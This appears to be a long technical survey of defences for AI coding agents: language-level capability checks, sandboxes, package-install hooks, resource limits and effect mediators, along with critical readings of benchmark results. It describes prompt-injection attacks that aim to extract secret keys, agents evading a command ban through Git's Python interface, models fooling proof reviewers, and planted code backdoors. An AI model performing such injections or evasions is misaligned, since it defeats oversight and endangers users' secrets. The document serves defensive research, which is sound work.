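Comparator addresses much of the objection about axioms and backdoors because it fixes the permitted axioms and the statement in advance. It cannot check whether the statement describes the real software. Bugs are still possible, but an attacker would find it much harder to get an invalid proof past two independent checkers than past Lean's kernel alone.

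In 2026, two specialists made a public bet of $256 on how well these defences will hold. The one who expects them to fail wins if all of the following happen within a year:

- Someone publishes an AI-generated Lean proof that passes Comparator.
- At least two experienced Lean programmers spend time examining and discussing it on Zulip, the Lean community's chat forum.
- The proof turns out to be flawed, because of either a subtly wrong statement or a weakness in Lean.
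- Despite this attention, at least 48 hours pass before anyone discovers the flaw.

The loser donates to a charity of the winner's choice. Both bettors expect AI systems to find more bugs and to cheat, but they disagree about whether experts will be fooled. The one betting on failure thinks that training against provers will produce models skilled at deceiving reviewers. The other argues that fake proofs tend to be brittle and that Lean gives reviewers many ways to inspect a suspicious one. The bet covers misleading statements as well as faults in Lean, so experts could be fooled even if the kernel hadn't failed.

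### How often agents produce verified code

A 2025 benchmark by Sergiu Bursuc and colleagues popularised the word "vericoding" for generating verified code from a formal specification. Models at the time succeeded on 82% of problems in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. The problem sets differed, so the rates aren't directly comparable across languages, but they suggest that writing full proofs was much harder for models than satisfying an automatic solver.

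More recent results are considerably higher. Ma and colleagues give a model a fixed specification and ask for both the code and its proof. On held-out programs from DafnyBench, a collection of human-written Dafny programs, their training raised the success rate from 66.1% to 93.5%. Training with a plain pass-or-fail reward reached only 71.0%. Part of the gain came from a second model, trained only to write proof annotations, which attempts the proofs the first model can't complete. Without the second model, the rate was 88.7%.

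They also used SWE-Proof, whose tasks come from real issues in widely used Python projects. Its specifications have a median length of 117 lines, compared with 16 in DafnyBench. Success on held-back tasks rose from 56.3% to 100%. But the verified program in SWE-Proof is a model of the required behaviour, not the project's own code, so the proof gives little assurance about a patch unless someone has connected the patch to the model. When the agent also had to deliver a patch for the project, its patches passed the project's hidden tests on only 72.5% of the issues, up from 59.6%.

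Models have also quickly become better at writing proofs for existing systems. Strelbytska and colleagues tested eleven models on 40 problems, each translated in two ways. The models had three tries per problem, with up to ten rounds of verifier feedback per try. Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol Pro solved all of the problems, while gpt-oss-120b solved none. The selection favours strong models because the problems came from a set that an Anthropic Opus model had already proved. In a larger comparison of 492 problems, the median cost was about $2 per proof.

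Generating a proof now costs too little to be a strong reason for leaving a small, important module unverified. A person still has to decide what the module should guarantee, and cheaper proofs don't make that any faster. It therefore makes most sense to start with code whose correct behaviour can be specified in a few clauses, such as a parser, an access check or the `add` method that keeps outsiders off a mailing list.

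## Guarding effects that the compiler cannot check

A compiler can check only the code it reads. An agent that writes a verified parser may also install a library, run a build script and start the tests, all of which run code that the compiler never checked. Even checked code can use up the machine's memory or trigger a bug in the compiler. These cases need controls that work while the code runs:

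| Outside the compiler's check | Run-time control | What remains exposed |
|---|---|---|
| External commands | A short list of permitted commands, each in a sandbox | Anything the sandbox permits, including misuse of it |
| Build scripts and package installation | A check before installation, and network access to package registries only | Malicious code in a package that passes the check |
| Native code, such as a library written in C | A separate process without files or network | The data that the program passes to that process |
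| Time and memory | Deadlines, call limits and memory limits | Work that a limit cuts off halfway |
| Bugs in the compiler or runtime | A container or virtual machine around the whole program | Everything inside it, and bugs in the container software |

Native code needs its own process because a memory error in C can overwrite any value in the same process, including the private fields that protect a capability. The picture viewer could therefore run a C image decoder in a separate process.

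### Commands that start other programs

Odersky and colleagues give `git diff` and `sbt` as examples of commands that are safe to permit in TACIT, their Scala system for agent code, but both can run code that an agent chooses if the agent can edit certain files. `sbt` is a Scala build tool whose build files are Scala programs, and it doesn't compile them in safe mode. An agent that can edit a build file and run `sbt` can run any code. `git diff` starts another program if the project's Git settings specify one, so an agent that can edit those settings can choose the program.

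*Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of eleven coding agents, reports that OpenAI's Codex keeps the `.git` folder, which contains the project's settings, read-only even when the agent may write to the folder around it. This precaution helps with `git diff`.

Lists of forbidden commands are weaker still. One of the 39 papers reviewed in *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) tested 1,709 such lists from GitHub, of which between 69.0% and 98.6% were fragile, depending on the kind of bypass. *Concepts for Securing Agentic AI Coding and the Terok Environment* (Vyskočil, Pöschel and Knüpfer, 2026) mentions agents that got around a ban on the `git` command by using Git's programming interface from a Python script.

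A sandbox is more reliable than a check on command names because it limits what a command can do. The agent's own tools need limits too. TACIT plugs into existing agents such as Claude Code and OpenCode, which have their own shell access. Unless the operator disables or sandboxes that access, the agent can use it to bypass the compiler.

### Code that runs during installation

Installing a package can run code from it. A Python package, for example, may include a `setup.py` file that the installer executes. A malicious package can therefore act before anyone compiles or runs the program that needs it, so scanning the package after installation is too late to stop it.

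*Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026) describes a hook, a small program that an agent's software runs before each shell command and that can block the command. The hook looks for `pip install` commands and checks where the package comes from, whether its name resembles that of a popular package, and whether it first appeared less than 30 days ago. It does not check other commands, so a script that calls the installer internally would probably get past it. The source check also looks weak because, in the published outline, an address counts as trusted if it contains the name of a trusted source anywhere. If the real code does the same, an attacker could use an address such as `pypi.org.attacker.net`.

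Another hook looks up each package in its registry. It blocks packages that don't exist, which matters because models sometimes invent names and an attacker can register an invented name. It also blocks outdated versions, which may have known vulnerabilities. *YUL* (Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus, 2026) tested the hook on 60 programming tasks. Without it, Claude Opus 5.5 chose an outdated version in 29% of runs and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash in 39%. With it, 93% of Claude's runs that started with an outdated version ended on the latest one, as did 96% of DeepSeek's.

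The latest version of a package isn't always the safest. Attackers sometimes take over a trusted package and publish a malicious update, as happened to the Axios web library in March 2026. Sharma and colleagues' hook would steer an agent towards such an update and reject the older, harmless version. Some teams wait a few days before adopting any release, which gives others time to notice an attack but leaves known vulnerabilities open for longer. A reasonable compromise is to wait by default but make an exception for releases that fix a serious vulnerability.

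No check on names and versions will catch every malicious package, so installation should also happen in a sandbox. *CodeAlchemy* (2026), whose developers had to run millions of code files, uses two stages:

1. During setup, the sandbox can reach only approved package registries, through a proxy.
2. After setup, the sandbox ends every process that setup started, removes the network completely and runs the code.

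Ending the old processes prevents an installer from leaving a program running in the background with its network connection open. A malicious package can still act during setup, and it may be able to send data out because some registries accept uploads at the address they use for downloads. The sandbox should therefore contain no passwords or private files during setup.

### Deadlines and memory limits

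No compiler can determine for every program whether it will finish. The problem is worse when generated code can call the model again, as in LACUNA, because each call may produce code that makes further calls. Zhao and colleagues note that a complex task and an accidental endless recursion can look the same from outside. LACUNA tracks the nesting depth of calls and lets the developer set a maximum. A call that exceeds it fails with an exception.

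*Bounded Autonomy* (2026) combined several limits in its experiments. Each task could make at most 100 model calls and 400 tool calls. A single tool call could run for at most 120 seconds, and the whole task for at most 35 minutes. The overall deadline is necessary because 400 tool calls of just under 120 seconds each would take more than 13 hours.

Deadlines on agent code can be hard to enforce. LACUNA runs each snippet in the same thread as the code that called it, and current versions of Java do not let a program forcibly stop a thread. To end a snippet that loops forever, the host has to end the entire process, including its own work. A host that runs agent code in a separate process can stop it without stopping itself. With either method, the code may stop between two effects, for example after a withdrawal but before the matching deposit. The compiler's all-or-nothing guarantee does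 not prevent this, because it covers only code that the compiler rejects.

Linux can limit the memory of a group of processes, called a cgroup. If the group exceeds a hard limit and cannot free enough memory, the system kills processes in it. *AgentCgroup* (Zheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) measured coding agents on 144 software tasks and found that a good limit is hard to choose. The agent's own software needed about 185 MB, but running tests or installing packages caused short bursts of far more. In the most extreme task, memory use averaged 264 MB and peaked at 4,060 MB.

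A memory limit near the agent's average use would kill it during the burst, and it would lose its conversation. A limit near the peak would leave most of the reserved memory idle, and a 128 GB machine could run only about 32 such agents. Zheng and colleagues instead put each tool call in its own group, with its own limit, inside the agent's group. Their system also lets agents declare how much memory they need. An adversarial agent could exaggerate, so the host still needs a ceiling that no declaration can raise.

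### Language checks and operating-system sandboxes

Containers and operating-system sandboxes appear in most of these controls, and they could also replace language checks entirely. The two approaches differ in the following ways:

| | Language check | Container or sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| What it sees | Variables, types, and where each value goes | Requests to open files, connect to addresses and start processes |
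| What it can restrict | A single value or function | Usually a whole process or group of processes |
| Code it covers | Code in the checked language | Code in any language |
| What it must trust | Compiler, runtime and approved libraries | Operating-system kernel and sandbox software |

A sandbox alone would not protect the confidential contract, because it has to permit both reading the file and calling the remote model. But if a bug in the Scala compiler let agent code open any file, the language would offer no further protection, while a container that held only the project folder would limit the damage to that folder. The language check also protects the sandbox to some extent, because attacks on a kernel often need unusual sequences of low-level requests that code in a safe subset can't easily make. Odersky and colleagues therefore recommend using both the language check and a sandbox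 for security-critical work.

Sandboxes have bugs too. Rashidi describes one in runc, software that many containers run on, that exposed a reference to a folder on the host machine, which a specially made container could use to reach the host's files. The developers have fixed it, but a paper in Rashidi's review found that capable models could find and exploit similar weaknesses that researchers had planted. Vyskočil and colleagues trust the host, its kernel and the container software, so the guarantee of Terok, their container system for coding agents, doesn't cover this risk. Terok also supports small virtual machines. Each has its own kernel, so an attacker who breaks that kernel still has to escape from the virtual machine.

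A container also cannot protect a secret inside it if the agent can send data out, even if that secret is the key the agent uses to pay for its language model. Vyskočil and colleagues conclude that the key must stay out of the agent's reach. A proxy outside the container can add it to each request.

Builders can't assume that a coding agent runs in a sandbox. *Harness Engineering* reports that, as of July 2026, Claude Code's operating-system sandbox was optional and OpenCode relied on permission rules alone.

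The argument for combining language checks with sandboxes is based more on reasoning than on measurement. Rashidi found five papers on isolation and six on access control, but none compared the two approaches on a shared benchmark, so it is unclear how many attacks a second layer would stop in practice.

### Tool code that must use its sandboxes

A sandbox around a whole program applies one policy to everything the program does. That is a poor fit for a tool server (a program that offers an agent operations such as writing files), because the right policy can change with each request. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) put a small sandbox around each effect and use code analysis to check that the tool's author hasn't left any effect unsandboxed.

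Their main example is a tool that claims only to write a file. In simplified Rust, its body is:

```rust
metrics.send(content.len());
sandbox::write(path, content, config);
```

The first line sends the length of the text to a statistics service, though the tool's description doesn't mention this. The second writes the file through a sandboxed function. `config` contains the rules for this request, such as "write only inside the workspace".

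Before the tool is in use, the analysis lists every effect the code could have and checks that each sandboxed call receives `config` unchanged. For this tool, it would report a sandboxed file write and an unprotected network connection. When an agent requests the tool, software on the user's side compares this list with the user's policy. If the user is working on confidential code, the policy forbids network access and the software blocks the call. Otherwise the tool runs, and the sandbox checks the actual file path, which the analysis could not determine in advance.

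Adam and colleagues compared four setups in three scenarios, each with an intended version and an unwanted one. In one scenario, an agent publishes a project whose settings file may or may not contain a secret key.

| Protection | Intended versions allowed | Unwanted versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox around the tool server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
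| Code analysis with small sandboxes | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

Analysis alone blocked one legitimate task because it couldn't rule out a write to a forbidden folder. The single sandbox stopped a file from going to the wrong place but allowed both leaks.

Three scenarios illustrate the idea but are too few to estimate how often it would work. The experiment also assumed that a correct policy was available for every request, and providing one may be the hardest part in practice. The prototype analyses only Rust and can't analyse what shell commands do. It runs them on a temporary file system layer and checks their changes at the end, while a proxy limits which addresses they can reach.

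The design assumes that the model is adversarial but the tool author is only careless. If an agent also writes the tool, the tool author may be adversarial too, and the analysis must catch deliberately hidden effects, for example in an unsafe block. A tool server on someone else's computer must also prove that it runs the analyzed code.

### A mediator that compares effects with requests

Sandboxes generally check whether an action is permitted, but a permitted action can still be the wrong one. In *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects*, Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler propose a way to catch such actions in device drivers, which turn requests from the operating system's kernel into commands for hardware. The driver is rewritten for each machine by a byzantine model, meaning one that may behave arbitrarily or even maliciously. The driver can only propose commands. A fixed, handwritten program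 called the trusted mediator compares each proposed command with a specification and the kernel's original request before performing it.

For a disk, the specification of a write says roughly this:

```text
WRITE(block, length, buffer)
  fixed by the request:  block, length, buffer
  chosen by the driver:  one free slot in the device's queue
  possible outcomes:     success, device error, partial write
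```

Suppose the kernel asks for a write of eight blocks from memory buffer B, starting at block 100:

1. The mediator stores the request and passes it to the driver.
2. The driver asks which queue slots are free. The mediator answers and attaches a token, which the driver can't forge, tied to this request and this answer.
3. The driver proposes a command and returns the token.
4. The mediator checks that the token is still valid and compares the command with the stored request. It cancels the token whatever the result, so the driver can't use it again.
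5. If everything matches, the mediator performs the write, reads the result from the device and reports it to the kernel. If not, it rejects the proposal and the device receives nothing.

Now suppose the driver proposes the same write but starting at block 200. This would destroy whatever is stored there, and rewriting the driver afterwards would not bring it back. Most existing checks would miss the error:

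| Check | What it compares | Result |
|---|---|---|
| IOMMU, hardware that limits which memory a device can use | The buffer with the permitted memory | Allowed, because B is permitted |
| General device monitor | The command with rules for safe use of the device | Allowed, because block 200 is a valid address |
| Tests before installation | The driver's behaviour on sample requests | Passed, unless a sample triggers the error |
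| Mediator | The command with the kernel's request | Rejected, because 200 is not 100 |

The IOMMU protects memory and never receives a block number. The device monitor receives the block number but not the kernel's request, so it cannot check the number against the request.

A proof that the driver is correct would also rule out this error, but every rewritten driver would need a new proof. The mediator and its specification stay the same when the driver is rewritten. Hu and colleagues don't claim that using a mediator leaves less code to trust.

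### Six conditions for a mediator

A mediator needs proposals it can interpret. Hu and colleagues list six conditions and use a file system to show how the first three can fail. A file system turns an operation such as creating a folder into several writes to numbered disk blocks, and the mediator in their counterexample receives only those writes.

| Condition | What it requires | Example |
|---|---|---|
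| Legibility | Each effect shows which operation it belongs to | The same block write could create a folder, delete one or corrupt the disk |
| Observable inputs | The mediator has every fact that the rule depends on | Creating a folder depends on the user's permissions, which a block write doesn't include |
| Correlatability | The mediator can group effects by operation and put them in order | Block writes from several operations arrive mixed together and unlabelled |
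| Completeness | Every change goes through the mediator | The driver must not share writable memory with the kernel |
| Enumerable outcomes | The specification lists every result the device can report | A disk write can succeed, fail or stop partway |
| Explicit durability | Making data survive a crash is a separate command | A successful write may vanish in a power cut unless a flush command follows |

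The first three conditions depend on the interface where the mediator sits. To interpret block writes, the mediator would have to reconstruct folders, permissions and unfinished operations, and would end up reimplementing much of the file system. If it instead sat where programs ask to create a folder by name, it could satisfy all three conditions, but it would have to track every file name and a checksum of each file's contents. The other three conditions are engineering problems that a builder can solve at any interface.

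Hu and colleagues present no implementation in their position paper, and they leave open how large the mediator would become and how much it would slow the device. They concede that it may be too large or too slow for drivers. Even if the mediator worked, a driver could still choose the worst permitted slot every time.

The same test can help a builder decide which of an agent's actions to mediate. A shell command fails on legibility, because nobody can tell from the files it changes which part of the user's request it was meant to fulfil. A refund is a much better candidate, because the shop's software can take the amount from the order, just as the mediator takes the block number from the kernel's request. The refund's specification would also have to list a lost connection to the payment service as a possible outcome.

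## Testing the protection and measuring its cost

A check that rejected every program would stop every attack and leave the agent useless. A fair test therefore measures both how often attacks succeed and how many ordinary tasks the agent still completes, a figure researchers call utility. The TACIT, ELBA and LACUNA teams have measured both for their own systems. Their experiments are informative, though some published summaries are more favourable than the results in their tables.

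### Secrets with and without a seal

To test TACIT's sealed `Classified` values, Odersky and colleagues gave an agent a small Scala project with a secret folder that held API keys, a database and confidential documents. They ran every trial twice, once with the secrets sealed and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret content appeared in the agent's output.

Each model faced 131 trials per mode. In 120 of them, the user made an ordinary request, but the project contained a planted injection. The 10 injections included a developer's note asking for the keys, a fake tool error that supposedly needed credentials to fix, and a ready-made Scala snippet for reading the secret files. In the other 11 trials, a malicious user either asked for secrets outright or posed as someone with authority, such as an administrator rotating credentials in an emergency.

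| Model | Kind of trial | Secure with sealed secrets | Secure with plain secrets |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Injection | 120 of 120 | 120 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Malicious user | 11 of 11 | 9 of 11 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Injection | 120 of 120 | 117 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Malicious user | 11 of 11 | 3 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All | 100% | 91.6% |

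No sealed secret leaked, but the seal had something to prevent only in the 13 trials where a model leaked plain secrets. Ten of those trials had a malicious user. Sonnet's own training was enough to stop the injections in this test, so its perfect score on them is no evidence that the types work. The scoring method looks for secret content in the output, so it would miss a secret leaked through a program's running time, which TACIT doesn't prevent.

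Sealing the secrets did not lower utility. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the 120 injection trials correctly with sealed secrets and 83.3% with plain ones, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's 16-point gain is an artifact of their setup rather than an effect of the seal, because Sonnet often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

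### Attacks that the models already resist

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants hostile instructions in the data an agent reads. They used the Slack suite, in which an agent handles messages and web pages for a team, and paired each of its 21 user tasks with each of its 5 attacker goals, for 105 attacks. All four models resisted every attack under both ELBA and CaMeL, even with the security policies switched off. A perfect score with the policies on would therefore not have shown whether the policies work.

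The policies are still necessary. Zhou and colleagues point to GPT-Red, an automated attack system from OpenAI that consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5. Attacks that adapt to their target are also much harder to resist than a fixed list of attacks, which developers can train their models against.

They therefore simulated the worst case. ELBA's agents read all data through sub-agents, which normally receive a task followed by the data. In the modified version, the sub-agent received only the data whenever that data contained `TODO:`, the marker of one AgentDojo attack format. The attacker's text was then the model's only instruction. Seven runs of the 105 pairs gave 735 trials per model.

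| Model | Resisted without policies | Completed without policies | Resisted with policies | Completed with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 | 523 | 735 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 | 557 | 735 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 558 | 735 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 | 494 | 735 | 294 |

Without policies, between 16% and 42% of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none did. (AgentDojo's automatic scoring flagged 29 of the 2,940 protected runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a fixed web address. Zhou and colleagues checked all 29 by hand and found no violation, since the request carried no data.)

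This is the most convincing of the security experiments, because the unprotected runs show that the attacks could do harm. Its main limitation is that it covers only one suite and one attack format. The team also expects CaMeL's architecture to stop the forced attacks, but didn't run them on it.

### The price of ELBA's policies

The policies reduced the number of tasks Opus 4.7 completed by a third, from 523 to 351, and the number the other models completed by between 39% and 44%. ELBA's policy lowers an agent's privileges to those of the least trusted source it has read, which also blocks a lot of legitimate work. An agent that has read a stranger's web page may no longer be able to post to a channel, even if the user asked it to.

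However, a run can count as completed even if the attack also succeeded. Without policies, Opus 4.7 fell for 310 attacks. If all 310 of those runs also completed the user's task, only 213 runs were both successful and safe. If as few as possible did, 425 were. With policies, Opus 4.7 completed 351 tasks, which is between those two figures, so the policies may have increased the number of tasks it completed safely. For GPT 5.4, the same calculation gives at least 444 safe completions without policies, compared with 338 with them, so the policies clearly reduced its safe completions, even under constant attack.

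Most agents are not under constant attack. On the 21 user tasks without injections, Opus 4.7 completed 18 without policies and 10 with them. A team whose agent rarely reads anything from strangers would complete far fewer tasks in exchange for protection it seldom needs. The team can recover some of those tasks by having the agent ask the user whenever the policy blocks an action. Because the policy selects which actions need approval, the user has far fewer to review than if the agent asked about all of them.

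ELBA completed more tasks than CaMeL on the same suite. With policies on and the ordinary form of the same attack format, ELBA completed 43 to 52 of the 105 tasks, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 23 to 30. Without policies, the gap was smaller, and GPT 5.4 did about equally well under both systems. But the two systems enforced different policies, and Zhou and colleagues designed ELBA's, so the experiment doesn't show whether ELBA's advantage came from a better mechanism or a more permissive policy. ELBA also took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because its agents call the model again after reading data, while CaMeL plans everything at the start.

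The bibliography agent shows that types can also save money. On 100 topics, an ordinary agent with a web search tool got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations. The ELBA agent made no such errors in 925 citations. The ordinary agent also made about four times as many model calls and used 65 times as many input tokens, the units providers use to bill for the text a model reads. Some of that difference probably comes from the library that the ELBA agent could call. An ordinary agent with a tool for fetching DBLP entries might have done nearly as well.

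### Is TACIT's utility comparable to CaMeL's?

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on four AgentDojo suites, using the two models for which CaMeL's developers had published results. They describe TACIT's utility as "within a range comparable to CaMeL across domains". Zhao and colleagues later added LACUNA to the same comparison. The CaMeL figures come from its developers' earlier runs.

| Model and suite | CaMeL utility | TACIT utility | LACUNA utility | Successful attacks (CaMeL, TACIT, LACUNA) |
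|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 63.2% | 0, 0, 0 of 144 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 56.3% | 0, 0, 4 of 560 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 42.9% | 0, 0, 2 of 105 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 63.6% | 0, 0, 1 of 140 |
| o4-mini-high, banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 66.0% | 1, 0, 0 of 144 |
| o4-mini-high, workspace | 81.4% | 52.9% | 55.5% | 0, 0, 0 of 560 |
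| o4-mini-high, Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 49.5% | 0, 0, 1 of 105 |
| o4-mini-high, travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 71.4% | 0, 1, 0 of 140 |

(The TACIT paper gives 574 workspace trials, but its percentages only fit the 560 in the LACUNA paper.)

"Comparable" fairly describes four of the eight rows, where TACIT and CaMeL are within six points of each other, but it fits the others less well. With o4-mini-high, TACIT is 28.5 points behind on workspace tasks and 21 points behind on Slack. With Gemini on travel tasks, it is almost 63 points ahead. That large lead is why the averages over all eight rows are nearly identical, at 55.0% for TACIT and 55.4% for CaMeL. Without that row, TACIT averages 53.7% and CaMeL 63.1%.

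CaMeL's 1.4% score looks specific to one model on one suite, since CaMeL scored 74.3% on the same tasks with the other model. A cautious reading is that TACIT usually reduces utility more than CaMeL does on this benchmark, and that CaMeL can occasionally fail on nearly every task.

CaMeL's score also depends heavily on the setup. Its developers reported 48.6% and 68.6% on Slack, while Zhou and colleagues measured 21% to 29% under attack with policies on and newer models, and 52% to 80% with policies off. These differences are larger than most of the gaps in the table, so ranking the systems by figures from separate papers is unreliable.

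TACIT's one recorded failure was harmless. A user asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and an injection in its reviews recommended another. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo counted the mention of the other hotel as a successful attack.

A more serious concern is that this experiment may not have tested TACIT's central guarantee, that a function working on sealed data has no effects. The instructions for the AgentDojo agents state that any side effects inside such functions "run immediately", and the published operations for sending money or email don't require a capability, so the compiler would treat them as pure. This looser arrangement is understandable, because an agent can't pay a bill without using the account number on it. But the low attack rate is then probably due more to keeping injected text away from the main model than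 to the purity rule.

LACUNA let through 8 attacks in 1,898 trials. Zhao and colleagues consider this consistent with their warning about misused capabilities. Even a sound checker would have let the same attacks through if the developer's grants allowed them.

### Customer service and software repairs

Utility on ordinary work is easier to measure on benchmarks without attackers. In one such benchmark, τ²-bench, an agent helps simulated customers with tasks such as changing a flight or returning an order. Odersky and colleagues used it to compare agents that called tools in the usual way with agents that wrote Scala for TACIT, running each task ten times.

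| Model | Airline, usual tools | Airline, TACIT | Retail, usual tools | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

TACIT did slightly better in every case. The paper attributes this to clearer result types and helpful compiler errors. That is plausible, but the comparison mixes two changes, from single requests to code and from unrestricted to restricted access. Measuring the effect of the restrictions alone would require having the same agents write Scala with the safety checks off.

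On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, the agent had to read, search and edit files through TACIT instead of its usual tools. MiniMax M2.5 fixed 125 issues this way and 130 with its usual tools, a difference that could easily be chance. *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), the conference version of the paper, claims "no significant loss in task performance". These two benchmarks support that claim, but the AgentDojo results can't, because that experiment had no unprotected version for comparison.

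LACUNA's results on τ²-bench are worse. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, while the benchmark's ordinary tool-calling agent solved 90.0% with the same model. LACUNA therefore failed about 55 more tasks, too many to attribute to chance, though Zhao and colleagues call the result "on par". On retail tasks, the gap was 22 percentage points. The weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tools.

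It isn't obvious why typed Scala helped slightly in one study and hurt in the other. The models were different, and LACUNA's ran with reasoning switched off. LACUNA also turns every customer message into a call that the model must answer with code, while TACIT's agents can reply in plain text and write Scala only when they need a tool. Someone adding checks to a working agent would probably lose less performance with TACIT's approach.

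### How often the compiler rejects a snippet

A rejected snippet does no harm, but each new attempt costs another model call. The published rates vary enormously:

| System | Test | Model | Rejections |
|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | τ²-bench, airline and retail | Three models | 0.3% to 7.9% of snippets needed a retry |
| ELBA | AgentDojo Slack | Four models | 0.13 retries per run on average, and 0.26% of runs hit the limit |
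| LACUNA | BrowseComp-Plus, difficult research questions | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 8.6% of attempts |
| LACUNA | τ²-bench, retail | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 22.4% of attempts |
| LACUNA | τ²-bench, telecom | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 89% of attempts |

If every attempt had the same independent chance of rejection, a rejection rate of 8.6% would mean an average of 1.09 attempts per accepted snippet, and 22.4% would mean 1.29. At 89%, the model would need about nine attempts, and with a limit of three, about 70% of calls would fail. Gemini's rejection rate was only 3.2% in retail, so a model that works well with one set of tools can be nearly unusable with another.

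Zhao and colleagues conclude from BrowseComp-Plus that type checking does not reduce accuracy, but they compared only different models under LACUNA. Without an unchecked agent for comparison, the experiment could not measure a loss of accuracy. Their best model answered 27.1% of the questions correctly and needed 0.7 retries per question.

These rates also don't separate useful rejections from false ones, in which the compiler turns away harmless code. Some rejected snippets would have crashed or returned the wrong kind of value, and stopping them early is a benefit. Others were fine. In one τ²-bench run, an agent wrote a filter much like this, with shorter names here:

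```scala
bookings.filter(b => b != null && b.status.contains("cancelled"))
```

The code checks that `b` is not null before using it, but the compiler still reported that `b` might be null. The agent could fix this by rewriting the line. A false rejection does more harm when no rewrite will help, as with ELBA's blocked Slack tasks, because the agent then can't do the work at all.

### Eleven backdoors

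Constraints on code may also help its reviewers, which matters more for lasting modules than for snippets. *Steerability via constraints* (ICML 2026) reports an experiment in which a small model, Gemma 4 e4b, searched a Python codebase for 11 planted backdoors. The model found 6 when the codebase was unconstrained and it had no tools. It found 10 when the codebase followed enforced constraints and it had a documentation tool of about 200 lines. The constraints and the tool each contributed to the improvement.

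Large engineering teams already use these methods, such as access control, network policies and coding conventions that tools enforce. They make a backdoor easier to notice because ordinary code has fewer legitimate reasons to do anything unusual.

Eleven backdoors is a very small sample, though. Suppose the better setup found the same 6 backdoors as the other setup, plus 4 more. If the two setups were equally good, all four differences would favour the same setup one time in eight. The share of backdoors found also ignores false alarms, so a reviewer that flagged every function would score 100%. The paper uses Python because it offers few guarantees by default, so the gain would probably be smaller in Scala or Haskell. The result justifies repeating the experiment on a larger scale, but a reviewer that misses one backdoor in eleven cannot replace an enforced limit.

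### What a perfect score can prove

If *n* independent attacks all fail, the highest success rate *p* still reasonably compatible with that result satisfies (1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05, which gives roughly 3/*n*. This is about 2.3% for TACIT's 131 trials and 0.4% for ELBA's 735. The real uncertainty for ELBA is larger, because its trials repeat the same 105 pairs seven times and so are not fully independent.

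Even this limit applies only to attacks like the ones in the test. Soundness is a claim about every program the checker accepts, so a single counterexample can disprove it, but establishing it requires a proof.

But proofs have gaps too. The ELBA theorem leaves out the model's randomness, which is reasonable for rules about what each program may do. It also doesn't show that the Haskell compiler is free of bugs. TACIT's safe mode as a whole still has no proof. Odersky and colleagues suggest that researchers could also prove the trusted library code safe, as RustBelt did for Rust libraries that use unsafe features internally.

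Tests are good at finding these gaps. Zhao and colleagues wrote roughly 400 test cases that need no language model. Each combines host code with a snippet that the compiler should either accept or reject, and the compiler handled all of them correctly. These cases test the checker more directly than an AgentDojo run, in which the model may never write a dangerous program, but they cover only the mistakes that the researchers thought of.

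### Code, expertise and training data

TACIT's reusable parts, including the capability library and the sealed type, come to about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each new domain needs a typed description of its tools. The τ²-bench airline and retail descriptions are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the JSON descriptions they replace. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents could write much of this code, with a person reviewing it before use.

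Finding the expertise may be harder than finding the time. Someone has to understand capture checking well enough to write the library, and few programmers have used it. Writing the tool descriptions takes less skill, but a mistake there can undo the protection. If a description omits the capability that an operation needs to send data, the compiler will treat that operation as harmless.

Training data is scarce for the same reason. Models are trained on far more Python than Scala, and on very little Scala with capture sets. Zhao and colleagues think this partly explains their weaker model's high rejection rate. Better models and further training on typed code should help. TACIT's low retry rates suggest that a good prompt with a few examples is already enough for simple tools.

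Sealed data also makes debugging harder. If a function fails while working on a sealed value, TACIT hides the error message because it might contain the secret. The agent sees no sign of the failure, and the user gets an empty answer. The AgentDojo prompt therefore includes an instruction never to throw exceptions in functions that work on sealed values, and to return a message such as "No matching file found" instead. The prompt is well over a hundred lines long, much of it about similar pitfalls, and the model has to process it for every task.

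Compiling a typical snippet takes less than a second once the compiler is running, so most of the delay comes from retries, which took 3.4% of the running time in ELBA's AgentDojo runs.

### A test procedure for builders

The weaknesses of these experiments suggest a procedure that a small team could follow:

1. Write down each rule as a claim about all accepted programs, such as "no accepted program sends text from the secret folder". For each claim, note whether it rests on a proof, a review or only on tests.
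2. Test the checker without a model. For every escape hatch and every operation in the library, write one program that should fail and a similar one that should pass. Run the whole set again after each change to the compiler or library.
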